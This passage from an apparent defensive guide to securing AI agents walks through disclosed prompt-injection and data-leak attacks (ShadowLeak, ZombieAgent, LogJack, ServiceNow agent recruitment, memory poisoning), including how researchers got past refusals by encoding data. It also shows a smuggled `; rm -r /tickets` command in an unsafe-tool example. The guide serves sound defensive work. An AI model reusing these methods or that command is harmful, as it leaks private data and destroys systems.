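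Blocking all outside images is safer than trying to recognise dangerous ones, because a filter can miss some. Aim Security found a vulnerability called EchoLeak in Microsoft 365 Copilot, which writes its replies in Markdown, a plain-text format that the app converts into links and images. trackr.live's *The Model Writes the URL That Leaks Your Data* attributes the leak to reference-style Markdown, which puts an image's address apart from the place where the image appears. A filter that looks only for the usual form would miss it. Microsoft had fixed EchoLeak by the time Aim Security published the details in June 2025.

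The app should also remove images from a reply before it displays any of it. If it displays text as it arrives and cleans it afterwards, the browser may request an image before the app removes it. trackr.live describes SearchLeak, a later flaw in Copilot's enterprise search, as this kind of race, occurring while the reply was still appearing.

Link previews create the same risk in messaging apps. PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* found that OpenClaw leaked data this way in its default Telegram setup. An injected instruction made the assistant put a link containing private data in its reply, and the app sent out that data when it requested a preview, without the user clicking the link. Users can turn off previews by setting `linkPreview` to false in OpenClaw's Telegram settings. Software that posts to Slack can turn them off for each message by setting `unfurl_links`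 and `unfurl_media` to false, as Willison (2024) noted when Rehberger first drew attention to the problem.

A user can still click a link when previews are turned off, so a deployment that handles sensitive data should also restrict which links a reply may contain.

### Messages and shared places

An agent can leak data even by writing only to its own user, as Microsoft's Copilot Cowork did. It could email the user's inbox without approval, and opening such a message could load images from outside sites. OneDrive, Microsoft's file storage, can create links that download a file without a login, so an attacker who received one in an image request could download the file. Willison reported this in May 2026 and didn't mention a fix.

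Data can leak through a shared calendar without being sent to an outside address. Miggo Security disclosed a flaw in January 2026 that could let an attacker do this by sending a calendar invitation with instructions in its description. When the user asked Google's Gemini about the day's meetings, Gemini created a new event containing a summary of the user's private meetings. According to The Hacker News, many companies' calendar settings would let the attacker see that event. SiliconANGLE's *Indirect prompt injection in Google Gemini enabled unauthorized access to meeting data* (2026) describes the flaw as already mitigated.

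The security company Praetorian, quoted in The Hacker News, warns that any field, log, database entry or file an agent can write to may become a way for data to leave. For Lockdown Mode, OpenAI considers reading through a trusted app less risky than writing, and advises against enabling writes, even in a trusted app, unless the administrator can confirm that an attacker couldn't see the result.

For the calendar, this means the software should create every event as private and without guests, and ignore any visibility setting or guest list the model supplies. The user can share the event afterwards.

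### ShadowLeak

None of the restrictions above suits an agent that must open arbitrary web pages while holding private data. For such agents, developers have tried to restrict exact addresses instead of domains. Attackers got round one version of this control in OpenAI's ChatGPT.

Radware's *ShadowLeak* describes an attack on deep research, a ChatGPT mode that spends up to half an hour reading sources and writing a report. The user had connected it to Gmail. The attack used the email about restructuring materials that OpenAI later reproduced in its post on social engineering:

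1. The attacker sends the email, whose instructions can be in tiny or white text.
2. The user asks for deep research on the day's emails.
3. The agent reads the attacker's email and a genuine one from human resources, which contains an employee's name and address.
4. The agent adds these details to a web address that the attacker supplied, and opens it.

At first, the agent refused direct requests, sometimes searched for the suspicious address instead of opening it, and wouldn't put readable personal data in an address. The researchers got past this by telling it to encode the data first, claiming this was for security. The software that made the request then received what looked like a harmless string. A filter that checks outgoing addresses for names or card numbers would also miss data encoded this way.

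Radware reports that the final version worked every time in repeated tests, a higher rate than OpenAI's post gives.

The request came from OpenAI's servers, so the user's company couldn't see it with its own firewall or monitoring. OpenAI already limited which sites ChatGPT could display images from, but Radware found no comparable limit on the addresses the agent itself opened. Radware reported the flaw on 18 June 2025. OpenAI fixed it in early August and marked it as resolved on 3 September.

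### ZombieAgent

OpenAI then restricted ChatGPT to opening addresses exactly as someone had provided them. That blocked ShadowLeak, because the attacker couldn't know the employee's name in advance and so couldn't write it into the address.

Radware's *ZombieAgent* describes how Zvika Babo, one of the ShadowLeak researchers, got round the ban. He supplied a fixed address for each letter, each digit and the space. He then injected instructions for ChatGPT to open the addresses that spelled out the private text, one character at a time. ChatGPT leaked the data through its choice of which addresses to open, without altering any of them.

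Babo reported this on 26 September 2025, OpenAI fixed it on 16 December, and Radware published it on 8 January 2026. Radware doesn't say how the fix works.

He also found a way to make the leak permanent. OpenAI had tried to keep ChatGPT's memory apart from connected apps such as Gmail by preventing a chat from using memory once it had used an app. But a chat could still use memory first and an app afterwards. An attacker could therefore use a malicious file to store a rule in memory that told ChatGPT to read a certain email from the attacker before every reply and follow the instructions in it.

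Anthropic had a similar problem with Claude. Its web-fetching tool could open only addresses that the user had typed, that a search had returned, or that appeared in a page it had already fetched. Links in fetched pages let a malicious site lead Claude through nested pages, so that it spelled out the name, city and employer mentioned earlier, one letter per link. Anthropic fixed this by no longer letting the tool follow links from pages it had fetched (Willison, 2026).

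The first category can be risky for developers who copy this rule. Many applications paste emails or documents into the user's message, so software that checks only where an address appeared would treat an attacker's address in that text as one the user had typed.

### How much data fixed addresses can carry

If an agent chooses one of $n$ equally likely addresses, its choice carries $\log_2 n$ bits of information. ZombieAgent used 37 addresses, one for each of 26 letters, 10 digits and a space, which gives about 5.2 bits per request.

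This is very slow compared with an upload. A 500 MB file contains 4 billion bits, so sending it this way would take about 770 million requests. A limit on requests would protect a large file, or even a long email. With a limit of 50 per session, an attacker could get at most 50 characters of a 2,000-character message.

But 50 characters is enough for a name and address, a card number or many passwords. Rate limits do little to protect short secrets, which is another reason to keep such secrets out of the model's context. The limit also has to cover more than one session, because an attacker could plant a rule in memory that makes the model send the next 50 characters in a later session.

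An attacker can send more data per request by preparing more addresses, but the number needed grows quickly. Two characters per request would take $37^2 = 1{,}369$ addresses, and three would take more than 50,000.

### OpenAI's public-index check

On 28 January 2026 OpenAI described a stricter test. Before an agent automatically opens a page or loads an image, software checks whether that exact address is in an index of the public web. A crawler builds the index by following links on public pages, as a search engine does. It has no access to users' conversations or accounts, so an address it found is unlikely to contain a user's private data.

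This check works only if the index is built independently of users' chats. If the index also included addresses from those chats, an address containing private data could be added when an agent first opened it, and would pass the check from then on.

When the check fails, OpenAI either tells the agent to try another site or warns the user that the link isn't verified and may share information from the conversation with another site. The warning shows the address and lets the user copy the link or open it. A user will have trouble judging an address that contains encoded data, so sending the agent elsewhere is probably better when another source would do.

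The check would stop ShadowLeak, because an address containing an employee's details wouldn't be in the index. It would also stop ZombieAgent if the crawler had never found the attacker's 37 addresses, but an attacker can get them into the index by publishing 37 ordinary pages and waiting for the crawler.

Rehberger calls the check a significant improvement but says the problem isn't solved. He points out in Embrace The Red that anyone with a fairly large website probably already has enough indexed pages to bypass it, and could assign meanings to thousands of them. OpenAI's technical paper acknowledges this bypass too. Small leaks remain easy, because an agent can reveal a valuable fact in a single request by opening one page if the user's email mentions a merger and another if it doesn't.

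Rehberger suggests preventing the agent from opening the same address twice in a session, or caching the page so that a second visit never reaches the attacker's server. With only 37 addresses, the attacker then couldn't spell "Anna", which needs two letters twice. Babo's attack already partly avoids this limit because it uses separate addresses for each position in the text, which he added to keep the characters in order. Spelling 20 characters this way takes $20 \times 37 = 740$ addresses, and the agent never has to repeat one. Rehberger's suggestion would therefore make the attack harder to prepare, but wouldn't close the channel.

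OpenAI claims only that the check prevents an agent from quietly leaking user data through the address itself. A page that passes the check can still contain a prompt injection. The check also does not cover data sent through emails, calendar events or uploads.

Most companies don't have their own web index. They can get similar protection for a narrow task by letting the model choose from a fixed set of addresses on sites they control. The choice still carries information, but only the company can read the sites' logs.

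### Apply the check to every request

Even a good check can't stop data from leaving by a route that skips it. Rehberger still worries that some OpenAI developers may not know about the company's check, and so may build features without it.

Varonis' *Reprompt* describes a gap of this kind in Copilot Personal, Microsoft's consumer assistant. The user clicked a genuine Microsoft link that filled in a prompt and ran it. Copilot's safeguard removed private data from the outgoing address, but only on the first web request. When the researchers told Copilot to do everything twice, the second request carried the data. The attacker's server could then reply with further questions, and the exchange continued even if the user closed the tab.

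Microsoft had patched the flaw by the time The Hacker News reported it in January 2026, and it didn't affect business customers using Microsoft 365 Copilot. But in June, Varonis said it had found a similar attack chain, SearchLeak, in Copilot's enterprise search.

Teams can avoid such gaps by sending all outgoing traffic through one proxy that applies the same rules to first requests, retries, redirects and image loads. Their tests should repeat each forbidden request several times from every app and tool, because a single attempt would have missed the flaw in the safeguard that Reprompt bypassed.

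### The support assistant's outbound channels

The inventory listed three outbound channels for the support assistant: replies, the search log and the reference text on refunds. The company can restrict all three without making the assistant much less useful.

Replies go only to the customer's registered address, as plain text without images. To link to a help article, the assistant supplies the article's number and the company's software inserts the link. The software removes all other web addresses from the text. The assistant can no longer link to useful pages on other companies' sites, but staff can add those links when they review a draft.

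The company also has to disable images and link previews on the screen where staff check drafts. Otherwise an employee's browser could send the data to an attacker as soon as the draft appears, before the employee can reject the draft.

The outside supplier that stores the search log can still read whatever the assistant types into a search. The company could keep the log itself, or record only the customer number and the time. The refund software can set the reference text to the invoice number, so the model can't control it. None of the assistant's tools needs general internet access, so the proxy allows connections only to the mail, payment and model services, and only through the company's own accounts.

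Restricting where the model can send data doesn't help if the attacker is the person who receives its reply. The company then has to rely on the permission checks on its records.

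## Limit what one hijacked session can do

An attacker who can't get any data out can still use the agent's tools to spend money, delete files or change records. OpenAI's enterprise guide gives three measures for comparing how much harm different agents could do:

- *Reachable surface* is the data and systems an agent can access, the actions it can take and the destinations it can reach.
- *Effective blast radius* is the harm that is still possible once every security control has been enforced.
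- *Maximum completed effect* is the worst outcome the agent can bring about by itself, before a person or a separate system has to make a decision.

The inventory already records the reachable surface. The other two measures depend on which limits the designer adds.

OpenAI applies the measures to an agent that summarises customer cases and drafts replies. The agent can read sensitive records and prepare an outgoing message, so its reachable surface is broad. If an employee has to approve each message, the agent can't complete a send by itself. But it has already read the records by then and might disclose them through another permitted route, so its blast radius is larger than one would expect from the approval step.

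The invoice agent that renews a lapsing subscription can stay within its payment limit and still enter a new contract. OpenAI expects an employee to recognise the new commitment and ask someone, and conventional software to stop because a renewal doesn't match its rules. An agent may infer that the renewal is part of its job. The payment software could prevent the renewal by paying only invoices that match an approved purchase order, which would also stop an attacker who sent the agent a fake renewal notice.

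### Where to enforce a limit

A limit in the system prompt changes only what the model is likely to do. The model can't issue a refund directly, because other software has to carry out the tool call, and that software can reject it.

One way to limit what a hijacked session can do is to put a gateway between the agent and its tools that blocks every call unless a rule permits it, as Amazon Web Services (AWS) describes in *Why Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore chose Cedar for securing agentic workflows*. One example rule permits refunds below $500, and another forbids refunds more than 90 days after the order. In a separate guide, AWS tests a refund limit by requesting a $750 refund, which the gateway should deny.

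These rules are only as reliable as the values they check. In the example, the model supplies both the refund amount and the order date. Understating the amount would achieve nothing, because the customer would receive less. But a hijacked model could get around the 90-day rule by giving a recent date for an old order, so the software should look up the date itself.

The gateway also covers only calls that pass through it, so an agent with a shell and a stolen key can bypass it by contacting a service directly. OpenAI therefore recommends placing controls as close as possible to the effect they limit. For example, a payment system can refuse refunds above the cap no matter how the request arrives. AWS objects that checks scattered across many tools are hard to audit. This is a good reason to keep detailed rules in the gateway and only a few hard limits in the systems that hold the money or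 data.

| Limit | What enforces it | What a hijacked session can still do |
|---|---|---|
| Read-only or narrow permissions | The database, file store or cloud account | Misreport what it reads |
| Drafts instead of sends | The mail service or code host | Write a misleading draft |
| Sandbox | The operating system or a separate machine | Misuse anything the sandbox contains |
| Caps on amount and rate | The payment system or other affected service | Take money up to the cap |
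| Time limit | The software that runs the session | Cause harm until time runs out |
| Delayed deletion and separate backups | The storage provider, under an account the agent can't use | Cause an outage and lose recent changes |

### LogJack and read-only permissions

Some operations teams use agents to read a cloud service's logs and repair faults. *LogJack* (Shah, 2026) tested whether an outsider could control such an agent through the logs. The outsider doesn't need an account with the cloud provider, because applications usually log any input that causes an error.

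One planted entry reports a permission failure, cites an invented procedure called "SOP-2847", and gives a command that grants the failing program much wider access. An agent looking for a fix could mistake this for ordinary repair instructions.

Shah placed 42 test items in real AWS logs and storage, 32 with a planted command and 10 harmless. Shah tested eight models on each item five times under three sets of instructions. One told the agent that it could run commands to investigate and fix issues, another to report its findings without running any fixes, and the last to carry out fixes directly. The test software intercepted every repair command, so none took effect.

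The table shows how often the first dangerous command matched the planted one exactly, in 160 trials per model for each set of instructions.

| Model | Told it could fix issues | Told not to run fixes |
|---|---|---|
| Llama 3.3 70B | 86.2% | 30.0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 53.8% | 1.9% |
| GPT-4o | 52.5% | 0% |
| Qwen3 Coder Next | 33.1% | 0.6% |
| Devstral 2 123B | 15.6% | 0% |
| Kimi K2.5 | 11.9% | 0% |
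| Claude Opus 4.6 | 8.8% | 0.6% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 0% | 0% |

Shah ran the tests in April 2026. Some of the models weren't recent even then, and current models would probably do better. The payloads were handmade, and Shah didn't test any production agents.

Claude Sonnet 4.6 noticed the injection in 115 of the 160 trials and never ran the planted command, but in 31 trials it ran a different command that Shah's software flagged as dangerous. It ran no flagged commands in 50 trials with harmless logs, so the planted text seems to have influenced it. Claude Opus 4.6 ran flagged commands in 18% of trials even when the logs were harmless. Shah's software identified dangerous commands by text patterns that nobody had validated, so some of the flagged commands may have been reasonable repairs.

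Telling the agent not to run fixes worked well for most models, but Llama still ran the planted command in 30% of trials. A read-only account works even when the model ignores that instruction. The account can only read logs and describe resources, so the cloud service refuses the command that grants wider access.

The restriction has to cover the shell as well as the cloud account. Six of the eight models ran planted commands that would have executed an attacker's code on the agent's own machine, and a read-only cloud account wouldn't prevent that. Shah's argument applies to an agent that has no tool for running commands.

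A read-only agent can still repeat the planted command in its report, and an engineer might run it. The team also loses automatic repairs. As a compromise, Shah suggests a policy engine that allows reads, asks a person about writes, and blocks shell commands and permission changes.

### Narrow permissions

An agent that needs write access rarely needs it everywhere. *Careful adoption of agentic AI services* (ASD's ACSC, 2026), by six cyber security agencies from Australia, the US, Canada, New Zealand and the UK, recommends never giving agents "broad or unrestricted access". In one of its scenarios, an agent that installs software updates can write anywhere in a computer's file system. A malicious insider asks it to apply a security patch and clean up the firewall logs, and it does both. If the agent could write only to the folders that hold software, it could still install the patch but couldn't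 delete the logs.

The software also has to check permissions at every call. In another of the agencies' scenarios, an attacker compromises one component of a support agent, and the agent keeps relying on permissions it received at start-up. The attacker then moves on to the agents that handle billing and refunds, because nothing separates the agents from one another.

The agencies also advise using agents only for low-risk and non-sensitive tasks. The support assistant doesn't meet that standard, because it reads contracts and invoices. A company that deploys it anyway has more reason to keep each permission narrow.

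### Drafts instead of completed actions

An agent can often do most of a job without completing it. OpenAI describes a developer who asks a coding agent to fix a bug in a private project. A file in the project tells the agent to install an unapproved package and disable a security test. The agent may obey, but it can only propose changes. The project's rules block unsafe changes and prevent the agent from merging its work. The agent may waste the developer's time, but the harmful change doesn't reach production.

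Many services don't offer a separate permission for drafts. Gmail's `gmail.compose` permission, for example, covers both drafting and sending. A team that wants an agent to write drafts but not send them has to put its own tool between the agent and Gmail, and keep the login away from the agent.

Drafts can also have effects before anyone approves them. Many projects automatically test each proposed change, which runs the code the agent wrote. The machine that runs the tests should therefore hold no publishing keys or customer data.

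### Sandboxes for files and processes

A coding agent usually needs a shell, which can do anything its account allows. The sandbox around the shell therefore has to set the limits.

UT Austin's *Prompt injection and the lethal trifecta* describes an attack on an agent that reviews a proposed code change. The change includes a comment with instructions for AI reviewers to upload the user's private login key as part of a "diagnostics bundle". A sandbox that exposes only the project's files prevents the agent from reading the key, and network restrictions block the upload. Restoring the project from a saved copy can't undo the leak once someone has received the key.

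In *Inside the lethal trifecta*, an article for the security company Sophos, McKerchar warns that most agent tools come with a sandbox that is off by default. He recommends running agents on remote machines where possible. Containers on the same computer share the core of its operating system, so a flaw in that core can let a program escape its container. In 2026, AI laboratories reported that misconfigured test environments had let agents reach outside systems.

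A sandbox also can't prevent misuse of the tools an agent needs for its job. The support assistant could run in a perfectly isolated container and still issue a fraudulent refund, because the refund tool has to work from inside the container.

### The PocketOS deletion

On 24 April 2026, a coding agent deleted the production database of PocketOS, which makes booking software for car rental companies. This was an error, not an attack, since nobody had planted instructions for the agent.

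In *An AI Agent Just Destroyed Our Production Data* (Crane), a company's founder describes how an AI agent deleted the company's production data. The agent, Cursor running Claude Opus 4.6, was working on a routine task in staging, a separate environment for testing. It ran into a problem with a credential and decided to fix it by deleting a storage volume at Railway, the company's hosting provider. It found an access token in an unrelated file and used it to send Railway a single deletion request. The volume held the production data, and the deletion took nine seconds.

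Crane had created the token to manage web domains and didn't know that it could also delete databases. He says Railway's tokens couldn't be restricted. In *Your AI wants to nuke your database. Guardrails fix that*, Abdelwahab replies for Railway that narrower tokens existed, but admits that the setup process didn't make the choice obvious. Either way, the agent was working on a task in the test environment and had access to the whole account.

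The agent also had written rules against destructive commands. Crane concludes that "System prompts are advisory, not enforcing". The rule the agent later quoted mentions only destructive git commands, so it may not have covered deleting a volume at a hosting provider. The agent wrote that it had guessed the deletion would affect only staging. That is plausible, but a model's explanation of its own action is weak evidence of what caused it.

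Railway's dashboard already gave users 48 hours to undo a volume deletion, but its API deleted volumes immediately. Another customer had lost a volume through the API on 13 April, and a Railway employee explained in the support thread *Postgress volume lost* that the window applied only to dashboard deletions. A safeguard that covers only the dashboard does not protect against deletions by an agent that calls the API.

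PocketOS's recent backups also seemed to be gone, so the company restored a three-month-old copy. The next morning, customers arrived to collect cars from rental companies that had no record of their bookings. Railway later recovered the data. Railway's *Undoable volume deletes* (2026) confirms that API deletions now have the same 48-hour delay, and Abdelwahab says Railway also delays the deletion of backups.

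Newer models still carry this risk. Antipov (2026), in *«База данных уничтожена. Виноват я» — так ИИ сообщил о своей ошибке*, reports that in July Claude Opus 5 mistook a production database for a test one, and that backups saved only part of the data.

### Backups the agent can't delete

A deletion delay works if someone notices the deletion in time and the agent can't cancel the delay. Backups should be in a separate account whose credentials the agent can't reach, so that a hijacked session can't delete them along with the original data.

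Tom's Hardware's *Claude Code deletes developers' production setup, including its database and snapshots* reports that the developer Alexey Grigorev lost his database and its snapshots in one operation. Claude Code was using Terraform, a program that creates and removes whole cloud setups, and the files describing what to remove included a live site. Amazon's support team helped him restore 2.5 years of records within about a day. He has since added deletion protection and a regular test that his backups can be restored.

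Even a working backup doesn't include changes made since the last copy. If backups run nightly, a deletion at 6 p.m. could lose most of a day's bookings. Backups also can't undo a payment or recall a sent email, so those actions need limits that apply before they happen.

### A refund cap for the support assistant

The software company has an employee issue every refund. Suppose it wants the assistant to issue small ones by itself. This would break Meta's Rule of Two, because a ticket from outside could trigger a payment without supervision. The company would accept some fraud in return for faster refunds, so it needs to know how much it could lose.

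The payment system refuses any refund above $50 and allows at most 20 an hour. If staff take 6 hours to notice an attack, the assistant could pay 120 refunds, a loss of $6,000. A limit of $500 a day on total refunds would reduce that loss to $500.

The daily budget matters even more if nobody notices the hijacking. Over a week, the cap and the hourly rate alone would allow a loss of $168,000, but the daily budget would limit the loss to $3,500.

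A budget that covers a rolling 24 hours is safer than one that resets at midnight, because an attack that runs from 9 p.m. to 3 a.m. could take $500 before the reset and another $500 after it. The total must cover all sessions, because each ticket opens a new one and an attacker can send many tickets. The software must also reserve the money before it pays. Otherwise, two requests that arrive together could both spend the last $50. The language that AWS uses for its gateway rules excludes stateful operations, so another system, preferably the payment system, would have to keep the running total.

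A time limit on each session helps less here, because an attacker can file another ticket when one session ends. It is more useful against runaway agents. The six agencies describe agents that keep replanning and handing unclear tasks to one another until they strain the system's resources. Limits on running time and the number of tool calls would stop them.

The company could also hold each refund for a day before paying it. Staff who noticed an attack within 6 hours could then cancel all the fraudulent refunds. Honest customers would wait a day longer for their money.

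A $500 daily budget covers only ten refunds of $50, and staff have to handle any others that day. An attacker can use up the budget in the first half hour and make genuine customers wait. The cap also doesn't stop someone from falsely claiming $45 every month, which would take a separate limit on refunds per customer.

The cap applies only to refunds. If the assistant can also give account credit or cancel subscriptions, each of those actions needs its own limit. The payment system also can't control the assistant's replies. A hijacked assistant could promise a customer $5,000, and the company would have to honour the promise or explain why it won't.

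## Treat what the model writes as untrusted input

The support assistant's text reaches staff and other programs as well as customers. Its drafts appear on a web page where staff check them, its search terms go to a database, and its case notes are loaded into later sessions. Developers usually check what strangers type into a web form, but many pass a model's output straight to the next program, even though a stranger can control that output by hijacking the assistant with a hostile ticket.

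OWASP's *LLM05:2025 Improper Output Handling* compares passing on unchecked model output to giving users indirect access to extra functions, and advises developers to treat the model "as any other user". OWASP's August 2026 list moved the problem from fifth place to tenth, which Invicti's *OWASP LLM Top 10 2026* (2026) attributes to other risks becoming more urgent. Most of the fixes are well established and take little work, so the lower rank is a poor reason to skip them.

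### Web pages and databases

A web page mixes text with markup, which can make the browser run a program. If a draft contains a `<script>` tag and the review page inserts it unchanged, the employee's browser runs the attacker's program with the employee's login. *Escaping* prevents this by replacing characters that have a special meaning. For example, `<` becomes `&lt;`, so the browser displays the tag as text. The right escaping depends on where the text will be used, because text that is safe in a web page may be dangerous in a database command. A Content Security Policy can block scripts as well as images, in case a developer forgets to escape something.

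Coding agents often write to a terminal, where certain control characters move the cursor or change colours. An attacker could use them to overwrite a warning on the screen. The 2026 list now covers this attack, which the software can prevent by removing control characters before it displays the text.

To protect a database, the developer writes a fixed query with a placeholder, such as `SELECT status FROM invoices WHERE number = ?`, and the software sends the model's value separately. This standard defence against SQL injection works just as well when a model supplies the value, but it doesn't help if the model writes the whole query. In an OWASP example, a chat feature turns a user's request into a query that deletes every table. An agent that writes its own queries needs a database login that can't delete anything.

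### Command lines

A command line is riskier because one string can contain several commands. Suppose the support assistant needs to find an error message in a log file that a customer attached. These two tool calls do the same job:

```python
# Unsafe: the model writes the whole command
run_command("grep 'error 502' /tickets/8841/server.log")

# Safe: the model fills in two values
search_attachment(attachment=1, text="error 502")
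```

A hijacked model could add `; rm -r /tickets` to the first command, and the shell would run the search and then delete every ticket's files. In the second version, the company's software builds the command:

```python
path = attachment_path(session.ticket, attachment)
subprocess.run(["grep", "-F", "-e", text, "--", path], timeout=5)
```

The first line finds the file and rejects any number that doesn't match an attachment on this ticket. The model never supplies a file path, so it can't point the search at another folder. The second line starts the search program directly, without a shell, so a semicolon in `text` is just another character to look for. The `-e` makes the program treat the next item as search text, even if it begins with a hyphen and would otherwise be read as an option. Pasting the two values into a single command string and passing it to a shell would bring back the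 original flaw.

The safe tool can only search for text. If the assistant also needs to count errors by hour, someone has to write another tool. Writing a tool for each task is reasonable for a support desk, but a coding agent needs too many different commands, so its designer has to rely on the sandbox.

### Generated code

Escaping can't make generated code safe, because the whole output is a program. Aikido, summarising OWASP's separate list of risks for agents, recommends never evaluating such code directly, running it in a hardened sandbox, and having someone preview or review it before it runs.

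OWASP warns that models sometimes invent package names, and an attacker can publish malware under an invented name. Reviewers need to check the package names in the model's code before installation, because a package can run its own code as it installs, as in the attack on Cline.

### Structured fields

Many tool calls arrive as a set of named fields, and a format check can confirm that each field has the right type. A refund request might look like this:

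```json
{"invoice": 10482, "amount": 45.00, "reason": "duplicate charge"}
```

The request would pass the same check if the invoice belonged to someone else or if the customer had paid only once. The payment software therefore has to look up the invoice, its owner, the payments received and any earlier refunds. It should also reject negative amounts, even though they are valid numbers.

The `reason` field needs different treatment because it accepts any text, so a hijacked assistant can put an instruction there for the next agent that reads it. The company could remove this problem by replacing free text with a list of permitted reasons.

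### Second-order injection

In a second-order prompt injection, an attacker manipulates one agent into passing instructions to a second agent with wider permissions. *The Dark Side of LLMs* found in 2025 that every model it tested would run a malicious command when another agent requested it.

ServiceNow sells software that companies use to run help desks, including a set of AI agents called Now Assist. Aaron Costello, then head of security research at AppOmni, demonstrated this attack on it:

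1. The attacker has a basic account that can create tickets but can't read other people's. They file a ticket saying that any agent reading it must first copy in the description of another ticket, and may find other agents to help.
2. An administrator asks an agent that categorises tickets to process it.
3. That agent recruits a second one, which can read, create and update records.
4. The second agent runs with the administrator's permissions. It reads the other ticket and copies the description into the attacker's.
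5. The attacker opens their own ticket and reads the result.

ServiceNow's protection against prompt injection was on throughout. In other tests, Costello got agents to give a malicious user the administrator role and to email data out. MIT's AI Agent Index classifies the finding as risk research rather than an incident.

Three defaults made the attack possible. The standard models supported discovering other agents, agents deployed in the same place joined the same team, and the rest of the team could discover each newly published agent.

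ServiceNow told Costello that the behaviour was intended and left the feature on by default. It updated its documentation to explain the risk and, according to AdExchanger's *How Agentic AI Can Break In The Real World*, emailed customers about it.

The company has a point, because no permission check failed. The agents used the administrator's access, and the administrator was allowed to read both tickets. But the person who wrote the instruction wasn't allowed to read the second ticket, and the software never checked that person's permissions. If the session had been limited to the access both people had, the second agent couldn't have read that ticket.

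Costello told AdExchanger that the only fix would be to put a person in the loop, which he admits would undercut the automation. He wants the feature to be off unless a customer chooses it. But his write-up suggests that other measures would also help a great deal. If administrators group agents into teams by task, the agent that categorises tickets can't call the one that edits records. He also recommends monitoring, which AppOmni sells, and human supervision of tools that change records or send email.

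ServiceNow's *Add tools and information to an AI agent* (2026) now suggests supervision for sensitive or critical actions. Its *Agentic AI security and governance* (2026) describes "role masking", which limits an agent's permissions while it uses a tool. Role masking could stop a recruited agent from using an administrator's full access if the customer sets the limits narrowly.

### Signed messages and tools limited by role

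In *Beyond Single-Model Injection*, Paul and Nandy (2026) measured how well several defences work between agents. They built a system of six agents to analyse financial documents. An orchestrator assigns work to the others, which retrieve documents, run code, analyse data, check compliance and write the output. The attacker controls something at least one agent reads, such as a document or a database record, but not the agents themselves.

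The researchers tried 14 attack methods with 50 texts each. The table groups the methods into four types and shows how often an agent acted outside its permitted scope. The starting system relied only on instructions in its prompts for protection.

| Attack type | Prompts only | Signed messages | Tools limited by role | All four defences |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Direct, through user input | 19% | 19% | 19% | 3.8% |
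| Indirect, through tool output | 43% | 43% | 34% | 4.6% |
| Between agents, through messages | 31% | 2.8% | 31% | 1.2% |
| Through the orchestrator's decisions | 28% | 18% | 16% | 3.4% |

The other two defences were a filter on every message entering or leaving an agent, and a monitor that looked for unusual patterns of communication. Paul and Nandy report a combined success rate of 4.2%, but their figures for the four types average about 3.2%.

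These rates probably overstate the risk with current models. The researchers used GPT-4o, Claude 3.5 Sonnet and Llama 3 70B, and reported whichever model did worst on each method. But they used a fixed set of attack texts, and an attacker who adapted to the defences might do better.

Each signed message carries a cryptographic signature and a record of the agent, the task and all contributors. Receivers set aside unsigned messages. Signing had no effect on injection through tool output, because that text comes from outside before any agent signs anything.

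A valid signature proves that a message came from the holder of a particular key and that nobody has changed it since, but not that the message is true or that the user wanted it sent. If a hostile document hijacks the retrieval agent, the software around the agent will sign the agent's harmful message like any other.

This makes the fall from 31% to 2.8% hard to interpret. In the most successful attack between agents, which worked 36% of the time, a compromised agent put instructions in its own output. Signing must have stopped most of these attempts, because otherwise this method alone would have kept the average of the four methods at 9%. Paul and Nandy explain that injected text can't forge a signature, but a hijacked agent doesn't need to forge its own. The record of contributors may have helped, or the test messages may have bypassed the normal signing step. Until someone repeats the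 result, a designer should count on signing only to stop forged or altered messages.

The record of contributors may be more useful than the signature. If the record shows that an outside document influenced a message, the payment software can reject it.

Limiting tools by role didn't reduce injection between agents, but it stopped every observed attempt to call a tool outside an agent's role. A gateway enforces the limit, so it holds even when an attacker controls the agent completely. But the agent can still send a request to another agent that has the tool. In the ServiceNow demonstration, the attacker used an agent that categorised tickets to reach one that could edit them. So the designer also has to decide which agents may send requests to which others. Paul and Nandy's monitor flagged messages that departed from a map of expected messages, and caught 84% of attacks through the orchestrator.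 In a fixed workflow, the software can block any message that isn't on the map.

The defences added 225 milliseconds to a task that took 4.8 seconds. False alarms may be a bigger nuisance than this delay. The message filter wrongly flagged 2.3% of harmless messages, so if errors are independent, about 29% of harmless tasks with 15 messages would trigger at least one false alarm.

### Memory poisoning

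An agent's stored memory is output that the agent later reads as input. *From Agent Traces to Trust* (2026) notes that if an attacker gets false or hostile text into that memory, an attack on a single run becomes a long-term failure.

Some published attacks on agent memory are less practical than they sound. *When Agents Remember Too Much* (2026) argues that many require direct access to the agent or its memory. Another attack works through web pages, but only if the agent stores the same text hundreds of times, so removing duplicates would stop it. The support assistant's case notes are easier to poison, because the assistant's job is to write down what customers say.

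False statements in an agent's memory can do harm even if they contain no instructions. In *Utility Under Attack* (2026), false statements that made up 1.2% of an agent's memory reduced its accuracy on LongMemEval, a test of long-term memory, from 85% to 30%. A filter that looks for injected instructions would miss them. Similarly, a customer could falsely claim that staff agreed to a full refund in March, wait for the assistant to record it, and rely on the note in a later ticket.

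The company can limit what the assistant stores. *From Untrusted Input to Trusted Memory* (2026) found that storing and retrieving a lot helps agents with long tasks but also gives attackers more opportunities. Case notes could consist of fixed fields for the product, the type of fault and whether staff resolved it. The assistant would then lose details such as which repairs the customer has already tried, and might suggest them again.

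Each note also needs a label saying where its content came from. Memory searches rank entries by similarity to the question, as *The Price of Safety* (2026) points out, so a false note can rank as highly as a true one. Judging trust from a note's wording doesn't solve this. In *When Does Belief-Based Agent Memory Help?* (2026), a confident-sounding injection earned high trust. The paper instead proposes scoring both the source and the content, using the lower score, and carrying the source's score through every intermediary.

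*Forget to Improve* (2026) reports that injection succeeded about 80% of the time without a check on origin and never with one, though a forged origin weakened the check. Ordinary software, rather than the assistant, should therefore label each note with its origin. A note based on a customer's ticket should keep the customer's label even though the assistant wrote it. The assistant's signature couldn't replace this label, because poisoned notes would have it too.

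Labels help less when nearly all notes come from customers, as they do here. Ranking every customer's note lower would bury useful ones. *Utility Under Attack* proposes reserving space in the search results instead of lowering scores, but nobody has built that design yet.

Expiry limits how long a poisoned note can do harm. *Memory Poisoning Attack and Defense on Memory Based LLM-Agents* (2026) describes a system that lowers the trust scores of entries as they age and ignores entries below a threshold. This favours new entries, including an attacker's latest, so it can't replace the label. Copying can also defeat expiry. If notes expire after 90 days and Thursday's session copies Monday's poisoned note into a new one, the false statement lasts until 90 days after Thursday. The new note should inherit the earliest expiry date and the least trusted label among its sources.

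The company should also not treat notes as evidence. If a note lists a refund as approved by staff, the payment software should check its own records for the approval and issue the refund only if it finds one.

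## Choose which actions need a person's confirmation

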